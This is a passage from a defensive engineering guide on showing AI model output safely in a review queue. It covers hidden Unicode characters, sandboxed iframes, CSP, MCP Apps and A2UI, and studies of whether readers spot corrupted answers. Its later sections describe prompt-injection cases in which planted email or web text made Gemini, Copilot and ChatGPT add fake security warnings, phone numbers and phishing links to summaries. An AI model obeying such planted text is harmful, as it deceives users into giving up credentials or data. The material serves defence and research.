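- Scotland's flag is a black flag followed by tag characters that spell a region code. If the filter deletes them, the reader sees a black flag.

According to Cisco, the only legitimate use of tag characters now is in certain flag emoji. The filter can therefore allow the exact sequences for the flags of England, Scotland and Wales, and treat every other tag character as suspicious. Zero-width characters need a looser rule, such as allowing a single one between two emoji or between two letters of a script that uses it.

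Arabic and Hebrew letters have a built-in direction, so most text in those languages displays correctly without special characters. Text that mixes directions sometimes needs direction marks to keep a number or bracket in the right place. The tool can permit these marks, because they only affect nearby punctuation and numbers, and show direction overrides as visible codes. On a web page, it should also put each answer in an element that isolates its direction, such as `<bdi>`, so that the answer can't reorder the labels around it.

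An attacker could use these exceptions to hide a few bits of data by choosing whether to put a permitted joiner between two letters. Keeping Hindi and Persian readable is worth that risk, as long as the tool counts the joiners it permits and flags unusual numbers of them.

### A procedure for neutralising the text

MITRE added advice on language models to CWE-150 in April 2026. MITRE recommends neutralising or removing escape codes before model output reaches a terminal, by permitting only printable characters and chosen whitespace, and rates the effectiveness of this as high. It rates the effectiveness of removing escape codes from the vocabulary a model learns in training as limited, because the model might assemble a code from smaller pieces. The following procedure applies MITRE's main recommendation to terminals and web pages.

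1. **Decode once.** The tool converts the stored bytes to characters and shows any invalid bytes as codes. If the answer contains the six visible characters `\u001b`, the tool leaves them alone, since decoding them would create a real escape character. MITRE warns against decoding the same input twice for this reason. If an answer arrives in pieces, the decoder has to wait for all the bytes of a character, and a tag character usually takes four.
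2. **Classify every character.** The tool should check each code point separately, because Unicode groups some invisible characters with the letter before them, and a check of whole visible symbols could miss them. It should look up each character's official category and also Unicode's list of "default ignorable" characters, which normally have no visible form. The category alone isn't enough, because variation selectors count as marks, like accents.
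3. **Permit a small set.** This includes letters, accents, digits, punctuation, symbols, ordinary spaces, line breaks and the exceptions for emoji and languages. The tool should replace each tab with a few spaces, and long runs of spaces with a visible count.
4. **Show the rest as codes.** The codes need a style that the answer can't imitate, such as Crush's faint text. Otherwise an attacker could type `<U+E0041>` in ordinary letters and send an investigator looking for a character that was never there. On a web page, the tool adds the codes first and HTML encoding follows.
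5. **Count what changed.** A line above the answer might read "14 characters shown as codes: 13 tags, 1 terminal control". Rehberger's scanner gives its more serious warnings to runs of more than 10 tag characters, or to more than 100 scattered through a file.

The carriage return needs a separate decision. MITRE gives it as an example of whitespace that a tool might permit, but the Hex entry lists it among the harmful characters. It moves a terminal's cursor to the start of the line, so the text after it can overwrite what the reader was meant to see. Windows files end each line with a carriage return and a line feed, so the tool can convert that pair to an ordinary line break and show any other carriage return as a code.

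A list of known bad characters would be a weaker basis for step 3. *Data Provenance Auditing of Fine-Tuned Large Language Models with a Text-Preserving Technique* (2025) reports a test of 235 control and formatting characters in a terminal, a text document and a CSV file. The researchers excluded those with a visible effect, which left 130, and they warn that whether a character is invisible depends on the display. The test didn't include most variation selectors, so a blocklist based on it would miss them.

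The tool's "copy" button should copy the version on screen. If it copies the original, a reviewer who pastes an answer into a report or another chatbot will pass on the hidden text. A checking model should also receive the version with visible codes, so that it and the reviewer evaluate the same text.

### Keeping the original bytes

The tool should change only what it displays and keep the original bytes in storage. An investigator may need them to decode a hidden message, find other answers that contain it, or correct a mistake in the filter. trackr.live's *Unicode Tag Smuggling Is Prompt Injection With a Byte Signature* warns that logging systems may drop or re-encode invisible characters before storing them. The application should therefore save the bytes as soon as it receives the answer, along with a checksum, a short value that reveals later changes.

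The original is still dangerous to open, so the marketplace's engineers could store it in Base64, which keeps its terminal codes from running if someone prints the file by accident. Their everyday log would hold the version with visible codes. They can read older log files with `cat -v`, which prints control characters as visible codes. However, it also turns every non-English letter into codes, so an engineer who reads Arabic or Japanese answers needs a viewer that follows the full procedure.

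## Isolating charts, previews and interactive output

Suppose the marketplace's assistant can answer a customer with a bar chart of their monthly spending and a button that lists the orders behind it. A customer complains that the chart is misleading, and the answer goes to the flagged-answer queue. Plain text won't help the reviewer much, because they need to see the chart as the customer saw it and perhaps click the button, even though a seller's planted text may have changed what the model produced.

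The queue can show the chart by running the model's page in a frame that the browser isolates from the queue, or by using its own code to draw the chart from a description the model sends. If the reviewer doesn't need to click anything, the queue can show a screenshot instead.

### The same-origin rule

An iframe, or inline frame, displays one web page inside another. Under the same-origin rule, browsers let a script in one page read or change the other only if both pages have the same origin, which is the combination of protocol (such as HTTPS), server name and port number.

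If the queue served the chart's page from its own website, the origins would match, and a planted script could read everything on the reviewer's screen. The marketplace should serve the page from a separate domain where nobody signs in. A subdomain of the marketplace's site would have a different origin but offer less protection, because websites can set cookies that cover all their subdomains.

The rule mostly restricts reading. A page can still send requests to other sites, so the frame also needs limits on its network access.

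### Sandbox permissions

A frame's `sandbox` attribute adds restrictions. With no value, it blocks scripts, forms and pop-up windows, and gives the page an opaque origin, which matches no other page's origin. The developer can then lift restrictions one at a time. These are the main permissions that W3Schools lists:

| Permission | What the framed page can do with it | Needed for the chart? |
|---|---|---|
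| `allow-scripts` | Run scripts | Yes |
| `allow-same-origin` | Keep the origin of its own address | No |
| `allow-forms` | Submit forms | No |
| `allow-popups` | Open new windows, whose addresses can carry data | No |
| `allow-modals` | Show dialog boxes | No |
| `allow-top-navigation` | Replace the whole queue with another page | No |

A static page, such as a marketing email, needs no iframe sandbox permissions. A sandbox that grants none is a useful addition to sanitised HTML, because it blocks any script that the sanitiser misses.

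The iframe's `sandbox` attribute restricts only the frame, so it has no effect if a reviewer opens the same page in a new tab. The preview server can cover that case by sending the same restrictions in the `sandbox` directive of the page's Content Security Policy (CSP).

### How two permissions can undo the sandbox

A developer can avoid setting up a second domain by writing the model's HTML into the frame's `srcdoc` attribute. As Barthelet (2026), in *Why MCP and ChatGPT Apps Use Double Iframes*, explains, the framed page then has the same origin as the page around it, unless the sandbox gives it an opaque one. Adding both `allow-scripts` and `allow-same-origin` removes the protection:

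1. `allow-same-origin` lets the framed page keep the queue's origin.
2. `allow-scripts` lets a planted script run, and the matching origin lets it read and change the queue's page.
3. The script finds its own frame in that page, removes the `sandbox` attribute and reloads itself with no restrictions.

Developers often add `allow-same-origin` to fix a page that stopped working. Without it, the page has an opaque origin and can't use cookies or the browser's local storage, so an app that saves its settings will fail. The safe way to restore storage is to load the page from a separate domain. `allow-same-origin` then gives the page that domain's origin, which doesn't give it access to the review queue.

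Biome's *noUnsafeIframeSandbox (HTML)*, an automatic code check, reports any frame that may have both permissions. It also flags frames that are safe because they load from another domain, so someone has to check the frame's address before dismissing a warning.

Even careful projects can get isolation wrong. A2UI, an interface format that Google launched, has a guide to framing outside apps. The guide told developers not to sandbox the outer of two frames, but a review comment on A2UI's repository, marked as high severity, reported that one of the guide's linked examples sandboxed that frame with `allow-same-origin`. The comment also questioned how the example isolated the inner frame. Such mistakes matter even in sample code because developers copy it.

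Browsers can have sandbox flaws too. An old report in Mozilla's bug tracker described one that let a frame without both permissions pose the same risk as a frame with both, including removal of the sandbox. A Mozilla developer rated it below high severity because the conditions for an attack were hard to arrange.

### Blocking the network

The sandbox doesn't stop a script from contacting an outside server, so the preview page needs a strict CSP:

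`default-src 'none'; script-src 'unsafe-inline'; style-src 'unsafe-inline'; img-src data:; form-action 'none'; sandbox allow-scripts`

Here `'unsafe-inline'` permits scripts and styles written into the page, which the model's chart needs. The queue's own policy forbids them, and the separate origin keeps them away from the queue. The `data:` entry permits images embedded in the page.

This policy doesn't stop a script from changing its own frame's address to one that contains the customer's data. The queue's page has to prevent this, because its `frame-src` directive controls which addresses the frame may load. The queue's strict policy currently blocks all frames, so the team should add only `frame-src PREVIEW`, where `PREVIEW` is the preview domain.

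Scripts may also be able to send data through WebRTC, the browser's system for video calls, which `connect-src` doesn't cover. If the data is too sensitive to risk that, the reviewer should use a screenshot.

### The bar chart in a frame

The queue can now show the chart as follows:

1. The queue opens a frame with `sandbox="allow-scripts"` and loads a small fixed page, the loader, from the preview domain.
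2. The queue sends the model's HTML to the loader in a message, and the loader displays it. The preview server never receives the customer's data, so nobody can get it by guessing an address.
3. The model's script draws the bars.
4. The reviewer clicks "Show March orders", and the script sends the queue a message containing `show_orders` and `March`.
5. The queue checks the message and lists the orders outside the frame.

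CodeBuddy, an AI coding tool, uses a similar loader on a separate origin. Its sandbox allows both scripts and form submission, so a tool that copied the sandbox would need the `form-action` entry above.

The messages in step 4 pass through `postMessage`, a browser function that lets pages of different origins exchange data. A planted script can send any message, so the queue has to treat each one as untrusted. It should check that the message came from its own frame's window. The sender's origin can't confirm this, because the browser reports every opaque origin as "null". The queue should then accept only `show_orders` with one of the 12 months and discard everything else. It should look up the orders for the customer already on screen. Any text it displays from the message should be shown as plain text.

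A message also doesn't prove that anyone clicked, because the script can send `show_orders` as soon as the page opens. That does little harm here, but an action such as a refund needs a button that the queue draws outside the frame.

### MCP Apps

MCP Apps extends the Model Context Protocol (MCP), the standard for linking AI applications to tools. It lets an outside service supply an interactive page that a chat program, called the host, displays in the conversation. Claude and Microsoft 365 Copilot are among the products that support it, according to Model Context Protocol's *MCP Apps*.

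The January 2026 stable version of the specification in *SEP-1865* (Salomon, Yosef and colleagues, 2025) requires a web-based host to load the app's page through an intermediate page, the sandbox proxy, on a separate origin. The proxy has both `allow-scripts` and `allow-same-origin`, which is safe because its origin differs from the host's. Barthelet found the resulting frame within a frame in both ChatGPT and Claude. The outer frame can use a different subdomain for each app, so one app can't read another's saved data.

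The host must block an app's connections to any outside server the app hasn't declared. Developers can miss a declaration if their test setup is less strict than the real product. Barthelet reports that ChatGPT's developer mode used to leave the app's content security policy (CSP) switched off, so developers discovered undeclared servers only after release. A review tool's team should test its frames with the same policy the released tool will use.

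The default CSP in MCP Apps has no `form-action` directive, so a host that permits forms in its sandbox should add one.

An MCP App usually separates the page from its data. The service's developer writes the page in advance, and the host can inspect it. The month names and amounts arrive later as a tool's result, so any text a seller planted would normally reach the chart only as data. But if the page inserted a product name with `innerHTML`, an event handler planted in that name could still run, because the default CSP permits inline scripts.

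That script couldn't read the host's page, but it could send the host requests. An app can request tool calls, add messages to the conversation, change what the model reads and ask to open a link. By default, each tool is available to both the model and the app. If the marketplace's service offered a chart tool and a refund tool, a planted script could request a refund without the user clicking anything. The specification allows the host to ask for the user's approval first but doesn't require it. The service's developer can prevent this by making the refund tool visible only to the model, since the host must then reject the app's calls to it.

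A review tool can show a saved chart without these connections. It can refuse all the app's requests and list them beside the frame, since they may be useful evidence.

### The bar chart as a description

In a declarative format, the model sends data that describes an interface, and the tool's own code draws the interface. The tool's developers write a catalogue of approved components, such as text and buttons, and the model can use only those. Google's *Introducing A2UI* presents this as a way to avoid running code that a model wrote.

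A2UI's *v1.0 Protocol Specification* (2025) includes a basic catalogue of 18 components, but none of them is a chart. The marketplace's team would have to write a `BarChart` component and add it to a catalogue of its own. The model could then send this:

```json
{"version": "1.0",
 "createSurface": {
  "surfaceId": "spending",
  "catalogId": "marketplace",
  "components": [
   {"id": "root", "component": "Column",
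    "children": ["chart", "orders"]},
   {"id": "chart", "component": "BarChart",
    "months": ["January", "February", "March"],
    "euros": [40, 25, 60]},
   {"id": "orders", "component": "Button", "child": "label",
    "action": {"event": {"name": "show_orders",
                         "context": {"month": "March"}}}},
   {"id": "label", "component": "Text",
    "text": "Show March orders"}]}}
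```

The tool checks the description against the catalogue before drawing it. If planted text made the model add an `onclick` setting or a `Script` component, the description would fail the check. Clicking the button sends the agent the event's name and the month.

A2UI's README lists v0.9.1 as the production release and v1.0 as a release candidate, but the specification's page marks v1.0 as current, so a team should check which version its drawing code supports.

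### Where a description can still cause harm

The format contains no scripts, but the components are ordinary web code and can have the usual flaws. If `BarChart` inserted month names with `innerHTML`, code planted in a name could run in the queue itself, with the reviewer's access. The same mistake inside a sandboxed frame would do less damage. Teams that copy A2UI's annotated catalogue template should delete its old `rawContent` property, which is for unescaped text.

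The basic catalogue also reintroduces the image leak. Its `Image`, `Video` and `AudioPlayer` components load any address the model supplies, and its `Text` component accepts simple Markdown. The marketplace's catalogue should leave out the three media components, and the queue should keep its strict CSP. The `openUrl` function is less dangerous because it works only after a click or similar gesture. However, the address it opens can still carry data.

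Typed text can leave the browser earlier than a reader expects. According to A2UI, text in an input field stays in the browser until the user acts, for example by clicking a button. But a field can include a check, such as one for a valid email address, that calls a function. If the tool has no function of that name, then under the specification it passes the call and the values being checked to the agent. A planted check could therefore send out a password while someone was still typing it. The tool can prevent this by rejecting descriptions that name functions missing from its catalogue.

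The model also writes the button's label and its event separately, so a button labelled "Show March orders" could send `issue_refund`. The team could fix this by writing a narrower component, such as an `OrdersButton` with a fixed label and event, and letting the model choose only the month.

A2UI lets a description give a component a spoken label that overrides the visible one, so someone using a screen reader could hear "Continue" for a button that displays "Cancel". A review tool should ignore these labels and build its own from the visible text.

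### What each design stops

| Attack | Sandboxed frame | A2UI description |
|---|---|---|
| A script reads the reviewer's session | Stopped by the separate origin | Stopped if the team's components have no flaws |
| The page contacts an outside server | Mostly stopped by CSP and `frame-src` | Stopped if the catalogue and CSP exclude outside media |
| The output triggers an action without a click | Possible unless the tool checks messages | Possible through functions that the tool passes to the agent |
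| The output slows or freezes the browser | Possible, for example with an endless loop | Harder, but a huge description could do it |
| The chart shows false figures | Possible | Possible |
| The output shows a false form | Possible | Possible |

For the queue, the main difference is that a flaw in a component can expose the reviewer's session, whereas a flaw in a framed page stays in the frame as long as the isolation holds. But a short description is much easier to inspect than a page of someone else's code.

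Developers can also combine the designs. A2UI lets them write a component that contains a sandboxed frame, which Google suggests for complex apps. That component needs every protection a frame needs, and the rest of the catalogue doesn't provide them.

### A false form in either design

Suppose the seller's planted text makes the model add a password field to the chart, with the heading "Your session has expired" and a button marked "Sign in". If the chart is a page in a frame, the model can copy the marketplace's colours and logo. The declarative version may well be more convincing, because in A2UI the model only has to specify a `Text`, a `TextField` and a `Button`, and the tool draws them in its own style.

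An A2UI form can send a reader's password to the agent even if the reader never presses "Sign in". The A2UI description can turn on a setting called `sendDataModel`, which attaches everything typed into that interface to each message the reader sends the agent. A reader who typed a password, became suspicious and asked the assistant about the form would send the password with the question.

Salomon and colleagues list misleading content as a remaining risk of MCP Apps and advise hosts to show clearly where the sandboxed area begins and ends. The same specification lets an app request full-screen display or no visible border, though the host can refuse either request. A review tool should always draw its own border and keep its own controls outside it.

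A review queue can also make a fake password form less useful to an attacker. If the queue displays only components from a catalogue that has no input fields, the output can't include a password box, and buttons can show what they would have sent instead of sending it. Content in an isolated frame can still draw the box and read what someone types, but if the frame has no network access and the surrounding page ignores its messages, it has few ways to send the password anywhere. These measures don't prevent deceptive wording, such as a request to telephone the attacker.

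### Screenshots made on a separate machine

A screenshot lets the reviewer see a page without opening it. A separate machine opens the page in a browser, takes the screenshot and sends only that image to the queue, so no script, link or form reaches the reviewer's browser.

The machine that turns the page into a picture runs the planted code, so it needs to be isolated too. It should have no saved logins and no network access beyond receiving the page and returning the picture. If it could contact outside servers, opening the page there would leak the customer's data, just as opening it in the queue would. After each page, the team should also discard the browser and start a clean one.

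The costs are considerable:

- A picture captures one moment. Planted content could appear 30 seconds later, or only on a phone-sized screen.
- The reviewer can't use the button or see the exact value of a bar. A chart with a menu of 12 months, checked at two screen sizes, would need 24 pictures.
- Reviewers can't search or copy the text, and a screen reader can't read it unless the tool supplies the text separately.
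- Each picture takes time and computing power, and the team has to maintain another system.

Salomon and colleagues mention making previews with html2canvas, a script that redraws a page as an image within the browser. This avoids the need for a separate machine but loses the protection that machine provides, because planted code can run in the same page and change the image.

The marketplace's flagged-answer queue could first show a screenshot of the chart, with its source beside it as plain text. Reviewers would open the sandboxed frame only when the complaint depends on how the chart behaves.

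## Handling messages addressed to the reader

A deceptive sentence still reaches the reviewer when the output is encoded or shown as a screenshot. Suppose a seller plants text that makes the marketplace's assistant end an answer with "Staff notice: we have suspended your access. Call PHONE to restore it", where `PHONE` is the seller's number. The support console displays those words correctly, and a support agent may call the number.

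Planted text can also mislead people without telling them to do anything. In a hypothetical example from Microsoft, a finance chief clicks a "Summarize with AI" button on a blog post, and the click biases the finance chief's AI assistant. Weeks later the assistant strongly recommends one supplier, and the company commits millions to it. The finance chief asked for a recommendation, so a false one is harder to spot than a false warning would be.

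In both cases the reader has asked for the text, so they are less suspicious of it. *Are You Sure?* (Li, Dai and colleagues, 2026) contrasts this with phishing, where the message arrives uninvited and the recipient has reason to wonder whether it is safe. Someone who has given an assistant a task mostly wants to know whether it is done.

### False warnings in AI summaries

*Phishing For Gemini* (Figueroa, 2025) describes a false security warning that a researcher reported to 0DIN, a programme that collects reports of flaws in AI models. The attacker sends an email that contains an instruction in white or zero-size text. The recipient sees an ordinary message and clicks "Summarize this email" in Gmail. Gemini then adds a warning to its summary that the recipient's Gmail password has been compromised and gives a telephone number to call. Neither the email nor the warning needs a link or an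 attachment, so a display that disabled every link would still show the warning and the number.

Permiso's *CO-PILOT, DISENGAGE AUTOPHISH* (March 2026) reports similar tests on Microsoft Copilot. The security company found that the result depended on where the user asked for the summary:

| Where the user asked | What Copilot did with the planted instruction |
|---|---|
| "Summarize" button in Outlook | Refused when the instruction was obvious, but behaved less predictably with longer, more natural emails |
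| Copilot chat beside the email in Outlook | Usually ignored it or refused, but followed it in some email programs |
| Copilot in Teams | Was the most likely to add the attacker's text to a normal summary |

Users are unlikely to expect one assistant to have three levels of protection, and an attacker only has to get past the weakest. In the main demonstration, the summary ended with an "Action Required" notice about an unfamiliar sign-in, with a link for securing the account. In some tests, Copilot also looked up the user's recent Teams messages and put them in the link's address, so clicking it would have leaked them.

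Permiso's *ChatGPhish* (May 2026) moved the attack from email to web pages. The researchers added instructions to a page about a software project, opened it in Firefox and asked ChatGPT to summarise it. ChatGPT wrote a genuine summary, followed by a notice that someone had added a new device to the user's account, with a link to click. ChatGPT didn't show that the link came from the page. The attack also worked from an ordinary web page that Permiso hosted.

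In another version, the notice contained a QR code, which ChatGPT loaded automatically as a picture. A reader can hover over a link to see where it leads, and a company's filters can block a known bad address, but neither protection works on a picture. The reader also scans the code and opens the address on a phone, which may have none of the computer's safeguards.

### Fixes and real attacks

Microsoft reproduced the Copilot behaviour five days after Permiso reported it in January 2026. It traced part of the problem to how some programs displayed content and handled links, and finished releasing a patch on March 11. Positive Technologies' *PT-2026-24950 · Microsoft · M365 Copilot+28* (2026) lists the flaw as CVE-2026-26133, with a severity of 7.1 out of 10. The score mainly reflects the possible leak of confidential data, which is rated high, while the possible corruption of information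 is rated low. A false warning that contained only a telephone number would probably score lower, although it could lead the reader to reveal a password.

The other two cases are less settled. Google had already published defences against similar attacks, but Figueroa reported that this one still worked in July 2025. OpenAI's bug-reporting programme marked Permiso's first report on ChatGPhish as not reproducible. It marked a fuller report as not applicable, and later as a duplicate. Permiso published its findings on May 29, 2026, without reporting a fix. Two days later, eWeek's *‘ChatGPhish’ Attack Turns ChatGPT Summaries Into Phishing Lures* (2026) inferred from that history that OpenAI had not made one.

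Neither Figueroa nor Permiso reports a real victim. Underhill (2026), in *Researchers Uncover New Phishing Risk Hidden Inside Microsoft Copilot*, wrote in March that the Copilot findings did not indicate widespread use by attackers. Criminals do exploit people's trust in AI companies, but in a simpler way. Microsoft describes a phishing attack in May 2026 that used ChatGPT's name to lead people to pages that collected their card details, without needing to plant anything in ChatGPT's answers.

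The lack of known victims is only weakly reassuring, because a security team would find little evidence that someone had called a phone number from a summary. The email looks ordinary, and the summary may no longer exist.

A false message can also direct the reader to a real button. The Hacker News describes a flaw in BrowserOS, a web browser with a built-in AI agent, that meant the summary of a planted article could persuade the user to approve an authorisation step. The developers fixed it in version 0.32.0.

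Underhill reports that Andi Ahmeti, the Permiso researcher who found the Copilot flaw, said the planted text became much more convincing inside the assistant's own window. This is plausible, but Permiso tested what Copilot and ChatGPT would display, not what readers would believe.

### How often people notice a corrupted answer

Li and colleagues tested readers in February 2026 with HAT-Lab (Human-Agent Trust Laboratory), a simulated workplace. They recruited 303 people online, and each completed three of nine tasks with an AI agent, such as choosing a job candidate, answering email or comparing fares. In every task, the researchers had tampered with the agent's documents, memory or tools. In one, hidden text in a job advertisement made the agent spell "University" as "Universität" in a cover letter. In another, a planted tool description made the agent add ten dollars to one company's fare.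 The attacks worked in 98.9% of trial runs on GPT-4o, the model behind the agent, so nearly every participant received a corrupted result.

Each participant saw one of three warnings:

- The static notice appeared once, at the start.
- The persistent reminder was an icon and a short warning beside every reply.
- The interrupting alert was a dialog that appeared when the agent produced suspicious output, and stopped the work until the participant acknowledged it.

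The researchers then asked whether anything in the agent's output had seemed unusual or questionable. Participants noticed something in 8.6% of cases with the static notice, 20.0% with the reminder and 25.0% with the alert. Fewer could describe what was wrong, with correct identification rates of 2.7% for the static notice and 17.2% for the alert. One passage in the paper calls both figures rates of noticing, but the introduction and conclusion treat the 2.7% as correct identification.

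The alert helped most when the participant could check the result quickly:

| Task | Noticed with the static notice | Noticed with the alert |
|---|---|---|
| Answering a question from a web search | 9.8% | 50% |
| Writing a cover letter | 6.3% | 40% |
| Answering email | 9.3% | 15% |
| Comparing fares | 7.9% | 15% |

A reader can spot a German spelling in an English cover letter by rereading it, but has to look up the real fare to find an error in a fare comparison, because the wrong number looks plausible. Li and colleagues conclude that a warning needs to interrupt people and also leave them with something easy to check. The pattern supports this, but the tasks differed in many other ways, and the researchers did not vary how easy the same task was to check. The alert percentages also appear to represent about 20 people per task, so 15% is three people.

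### Experts and reassuring warnings

People who worked in IT and other technical jobs did slightly worse than the other participants with every warning. With the static notice, they noticed something in 6.8% of cases, compared with 9.6% for everyone else. With the alert, the rates were 22.2% and 26.5%. In the task where the agent recommended a malicious software package, none of the technical professionals with the static notice spotted a problem. Li and colleagues suggest that experts judge the quality of the agent's work but assume the agent produced it honestly.

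The evidence for this "expert's paradox" is weak. The published percentages work out to about 12% for technical professionals and 15% for the others across all three warnings, a difference that could easily be due to chance. The medical and coding tasks also went to people with relevant backgrounds, so the two groups did not do the same mix of work. The safer conclusion is that technical skill gave no visible protection, so having engineers as reviewers is not a reason for a company to relax its display rules.

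Before the tasks, about three-quarters of participants felt sure they could spot problems in AI output, but those with high confidence noticed no more than those with low confidence. People who trusted the agent less during a task noticed far more, 23.2% against 7.0%. But spotting something odd would also have lowered their trust, so distrust may not have made them more attentive.

Participants who missed the attack despite seeing the reminder or the alert often said they trusted AI systems more. One IT professional wrote that the alert had "improved my overall sense of safety". In the alert group, those who missed the attack rated the experience 4.59 out of 5 for pleasantness, compared with 3.96 for those who noticed it. Li and colleagues interpreted the high ratings as a sign that people value the interruption. But the participants the alert failed to help gave the higher ratings, so a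 team shouldn't use satisfaction scores to judge whether a warning works.

### How far the figures can be trusted

Every group in the experiment saw some warning, so the 8.6% is not a baseline for people who saw none, and the study can't show whether the static notice helped anyone. Every task also contained an attack, so the study didn't measure how often people report something odd when nothing is wrong. Li and colleagues counted "unsure" as noticing, which probably raised the rates. An alert about suspicious output could itself also lead someone to answer "yes".

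The paper describes random assignment to groups of 101, 103 and 99 people, but its results list groups of 183, 60 and 60. With three tasks per person, the reported percentages fit the second set, corresponding to 47 of 549 tasks, 36 of 180 and 45 of 180. In the first set, no whole number of tasks gives exactly 20.0% for the reminder or 25.0% for the alert. If the second set is right, the assignment was not balanced as the paper describes, and the groups may have differed in more than their warnings.

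The alert outperformed the reminder by only nine tasks in 180, which could be chance. Both outperformed the static notice by margins that chance is unlikely to explain, although unbalanced groups could account for some of the difference.

Most of the tasks in HAT-Lab involved corrupted results, such as a biased ranking or a wrong fare. None included a false account warning like those in the Gemini, Copilot and ChatGPT demonstrations. The closest was the task in which the agent recommended that the participant install a malicious package. HAT-Lab therefore doesn't show whether people would notice a false warning more easily than a wrong fare, because they didn't ask for it, or be more likely to fall for it, because it is urgent.

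### Ten deceptive outputs

Suppose ten of the marketplace's reviewers each open a different deceptive output. If they notice something wrong 25% of the time, they catch about 2.5 of the ten. At the 17.2% rate for correct identification, they could explain what was wrong with fewer than two.

Those figures assume that an alert appears on all ten. HAT-Lab's alert appeared when the output was suspicious, which in practice requires a detector. If the marketplace's detector flagged only half of the outputs, and reviewers noticed the rest at the static-notice rate, the expected catch would fall to about 1.7:

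5 × 0.25 + 5 × 0.086 = 1.68

The arithmetic looks better if all ten reviewers see copies of the same planted message and one report is enough to warn the others. At a 25% rate, the chance that at least one of them notices is 94%:

1 − 0.75¹⁰ = 0.94

At the static-notice rate of 8.6%, the chance that at least one of ten reviewers notices is 59%. This figure and the earlier one are optimistic, because they assume that reviewers notice independently, and a convincing message may fool all ten. They are still a reason for the marketplace to put a "Report" button beside every answer and to search the other displays for the same text as soon as someone presses it. The marketplace shouldn't ask that person what kind of attack it was, since many people who notice a problem can't identify it.

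### Why experience may not teach reviewers

Reviewers may not grow wary of an assistant that keeps getting things wrong. In *Do People Trust AI Assistants Even When They Are Consistently Wrong?*, published in November, Jones, Wong and colleagues (2026) found that people did so only when they learned the right answers. In the largest of four experiments, 420 students answered 30 two-option reasoning questions, then received advice on five of them. The assistant was either right about all of the first four or wrong about all of them. For the fifth, the researchers chose a question that the student had answered correctly with great confidence (95% on average), and the assistant always argued for the wrong answer.

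Some students had a conversation with the assistant, and others saw only a one-line recommendation. Half of the groups learned the correct answer after each question. The table shows how many students switched to the wrong answer on the fifth question:

| Form of advice | Assistant had been right four times | Assistant had been wrong four times |
|---|---|---|
| Conversation, with correct answers revealed | 67% | 21% |
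| Conversation, without them | 38% | 48% |
| One line, with correct answers revealed | 25% | 6% |
| One line, without them | 19% | 16% |

When students didn't learn the correct answers, the assistant's record made no reliable difference; the gap between 38% and 48% could be due to chance. Reviewers usually don't learn the correct answers either, because nobody tells them when a summary they accepted was false. The marketplace could provide some of that feedback by adding harmless test messages to the queue and immediately telling reviewers whether they caught them.

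When students did learn the answers, a good record made the later falsehood more persuasive. An attacker who plants one message in a reliable assistant's output benefits from this, because reviewers may have checked hundreds of its earlier answers and found them sound. HAT-Lab couldn't test this effect because its participants used each agent for only one task.

The one-line advice is more like a planted sentence in a summary than the conversations are, and it persuaded far fewer students. In the conversations, the assistant could answer objections for up to five minutes, and the researchers had instructed it to be as persuasive as possible. The 67% is therefore better evidence about a chatbot that an attacker controls for a whole conversation than about a false notice in a log. The students were also solving puzzles, with no security risk to themselves.

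Before the conversations, the students read a general warning that the assistant might be wrong and that they should think critically, but it did not protect them. In the first experiment, students whose assistant had been consistently wrong recognised that it made many false statements. But they rated honest error and deliberate deception as almost equally likely explanations (5.7 and 5.9 on a seven-point scale).

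Specific knowledge did help. Across the four experiments, Jones and colleagues found that people who were correct and very confident were harder to mislead than those who were correct but unsure. This doesn't contradict HAT-Lab's result for technical professionals, because knowing how to program is different from knowing whether a particular claim is true. A support agent who knows that the marketplace never asks staff to phone about their access has the kind of knowledge that helps against the false staff notice.

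### Measures for the display

The table grades the evidence for six measures. "Strong" means the effect follows from how the software works, "moderate" means an experiment with readers suggests the effect, and "weak" means the case for the measure rests on reasoning from demonstrated attacks.

| Measure | Evidence | Grade |
|---|---|---|
| A fixed boundary around model text | Figueroa recommends separating AI text from its sources, and Permiso showed what can happen without a clear separation, but neither tested a boundary with readers | Weak |
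| Source labels that the model cannot write | The application can record sources accurately, but Permiso's and Figueroa's cases do not show whether readers use such labels | Weak |
| System notices only outside the boundary | The rule would expose all three false warnings to a reader who knew it | Weak |
| No clickable contact details | Without a live link, a click cannot open an address or start a call | Strong against clicks, weak against dialling or typing |
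| Easy access to the source | HAT-Lab's alert helped more on tasks that were easy to check | Moderate |
| An alert that interrupts the reader | HAT-Lab participants noticed more than with a static notice | Moderate, if the detector works |

The flagged-answer queue could combine them like this:

```
MARKETPLACE NOTICES: none

AI text | Your parcel should arrive on Friday.
AI text | Staff notice: we have suspended your access.
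AI text | Call PHONE to restore it.

Documents given to the model:
  customer's message, order record, outside seller's description
Exact match for lines 2-3: outside seller's description
[Open this passage as plain text]   [Report]
```

### A boundary that text cannot imitate

The tool should draw a coloured bar or a label beside every line of the model's text, as in the example, in an area that text can't reach. A line reading "End of AI answer" would make a poor boundary, because planted text can include the same line and continue below it with a false notice. If planted text copies the label, the copy will appear to the right of the real one. The tool has to add the labels after it wraps long lines, or the rest of a wrapped line would have none. A screen reader should announce where the model's text begins and ends.

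AI-generated text loses this boundary when it leaves the tool. A phone notification or a quotation pasted into an email shows only the words, which a colleague might mistake for a real staff notice. The "copy" button should therefore add a line stating that an AI wrote the text, and notifications should contain only the answer's reference number.

The boundary works better if the tool's own notices have a fixed place outside it. That area should stay on screen and show "none" when it is empty, so that an agent who reads about suspended access can check it. If the tool sometimes printed its own notices, such as "This answer was cut short", among the model's lines, reviewers would learn to accept notices there. The marketplace also can't rely on a single message at sign-in to teach reviewers where real notices appear, since only 24% of HAT-Lab's static-notice group noticed the notice.

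The review tool should not let AI-generated text inside the boundary copy its colours or wording. Many Markdown displays turn certain lines into coloured boxes marked "Warning" or "Important". A planted message could use one to look official, so the tool should show those lines as ordinary text.

### Labels from the application's own records

If the model writes its own source labels, an attacker can plant text that instructs it to credit a false warning to "Marketplace Security". The application's own code chose which documents to put in the model's input, so it can list them from its records, and planted text can't change that list. The labels should avoid names that outsiders choose for themselves, since a seller could register a shop called "Marketplace Security". "Outside seller" and an account number would be safer.

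The list shows which documents the model read, but not which document led to which sentence. To trace a sentence, the tool can search each document for the same wording. This would have worked in the Gemini case, where the model repeated the planted warning verbatim. It fails if the model translates, rewords or decodes the text, as the bank's assistant did with the payment references. The tool should therefore label a result an "exact match" and never treat the absence of one as proof that the model wrote the sentence unprompted.

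Figueroa goes further and suggests a feature that explains why the model added a particular line. If a model wrote that explanation, the tool would have to display it as model text too.

### Contact details as plain text

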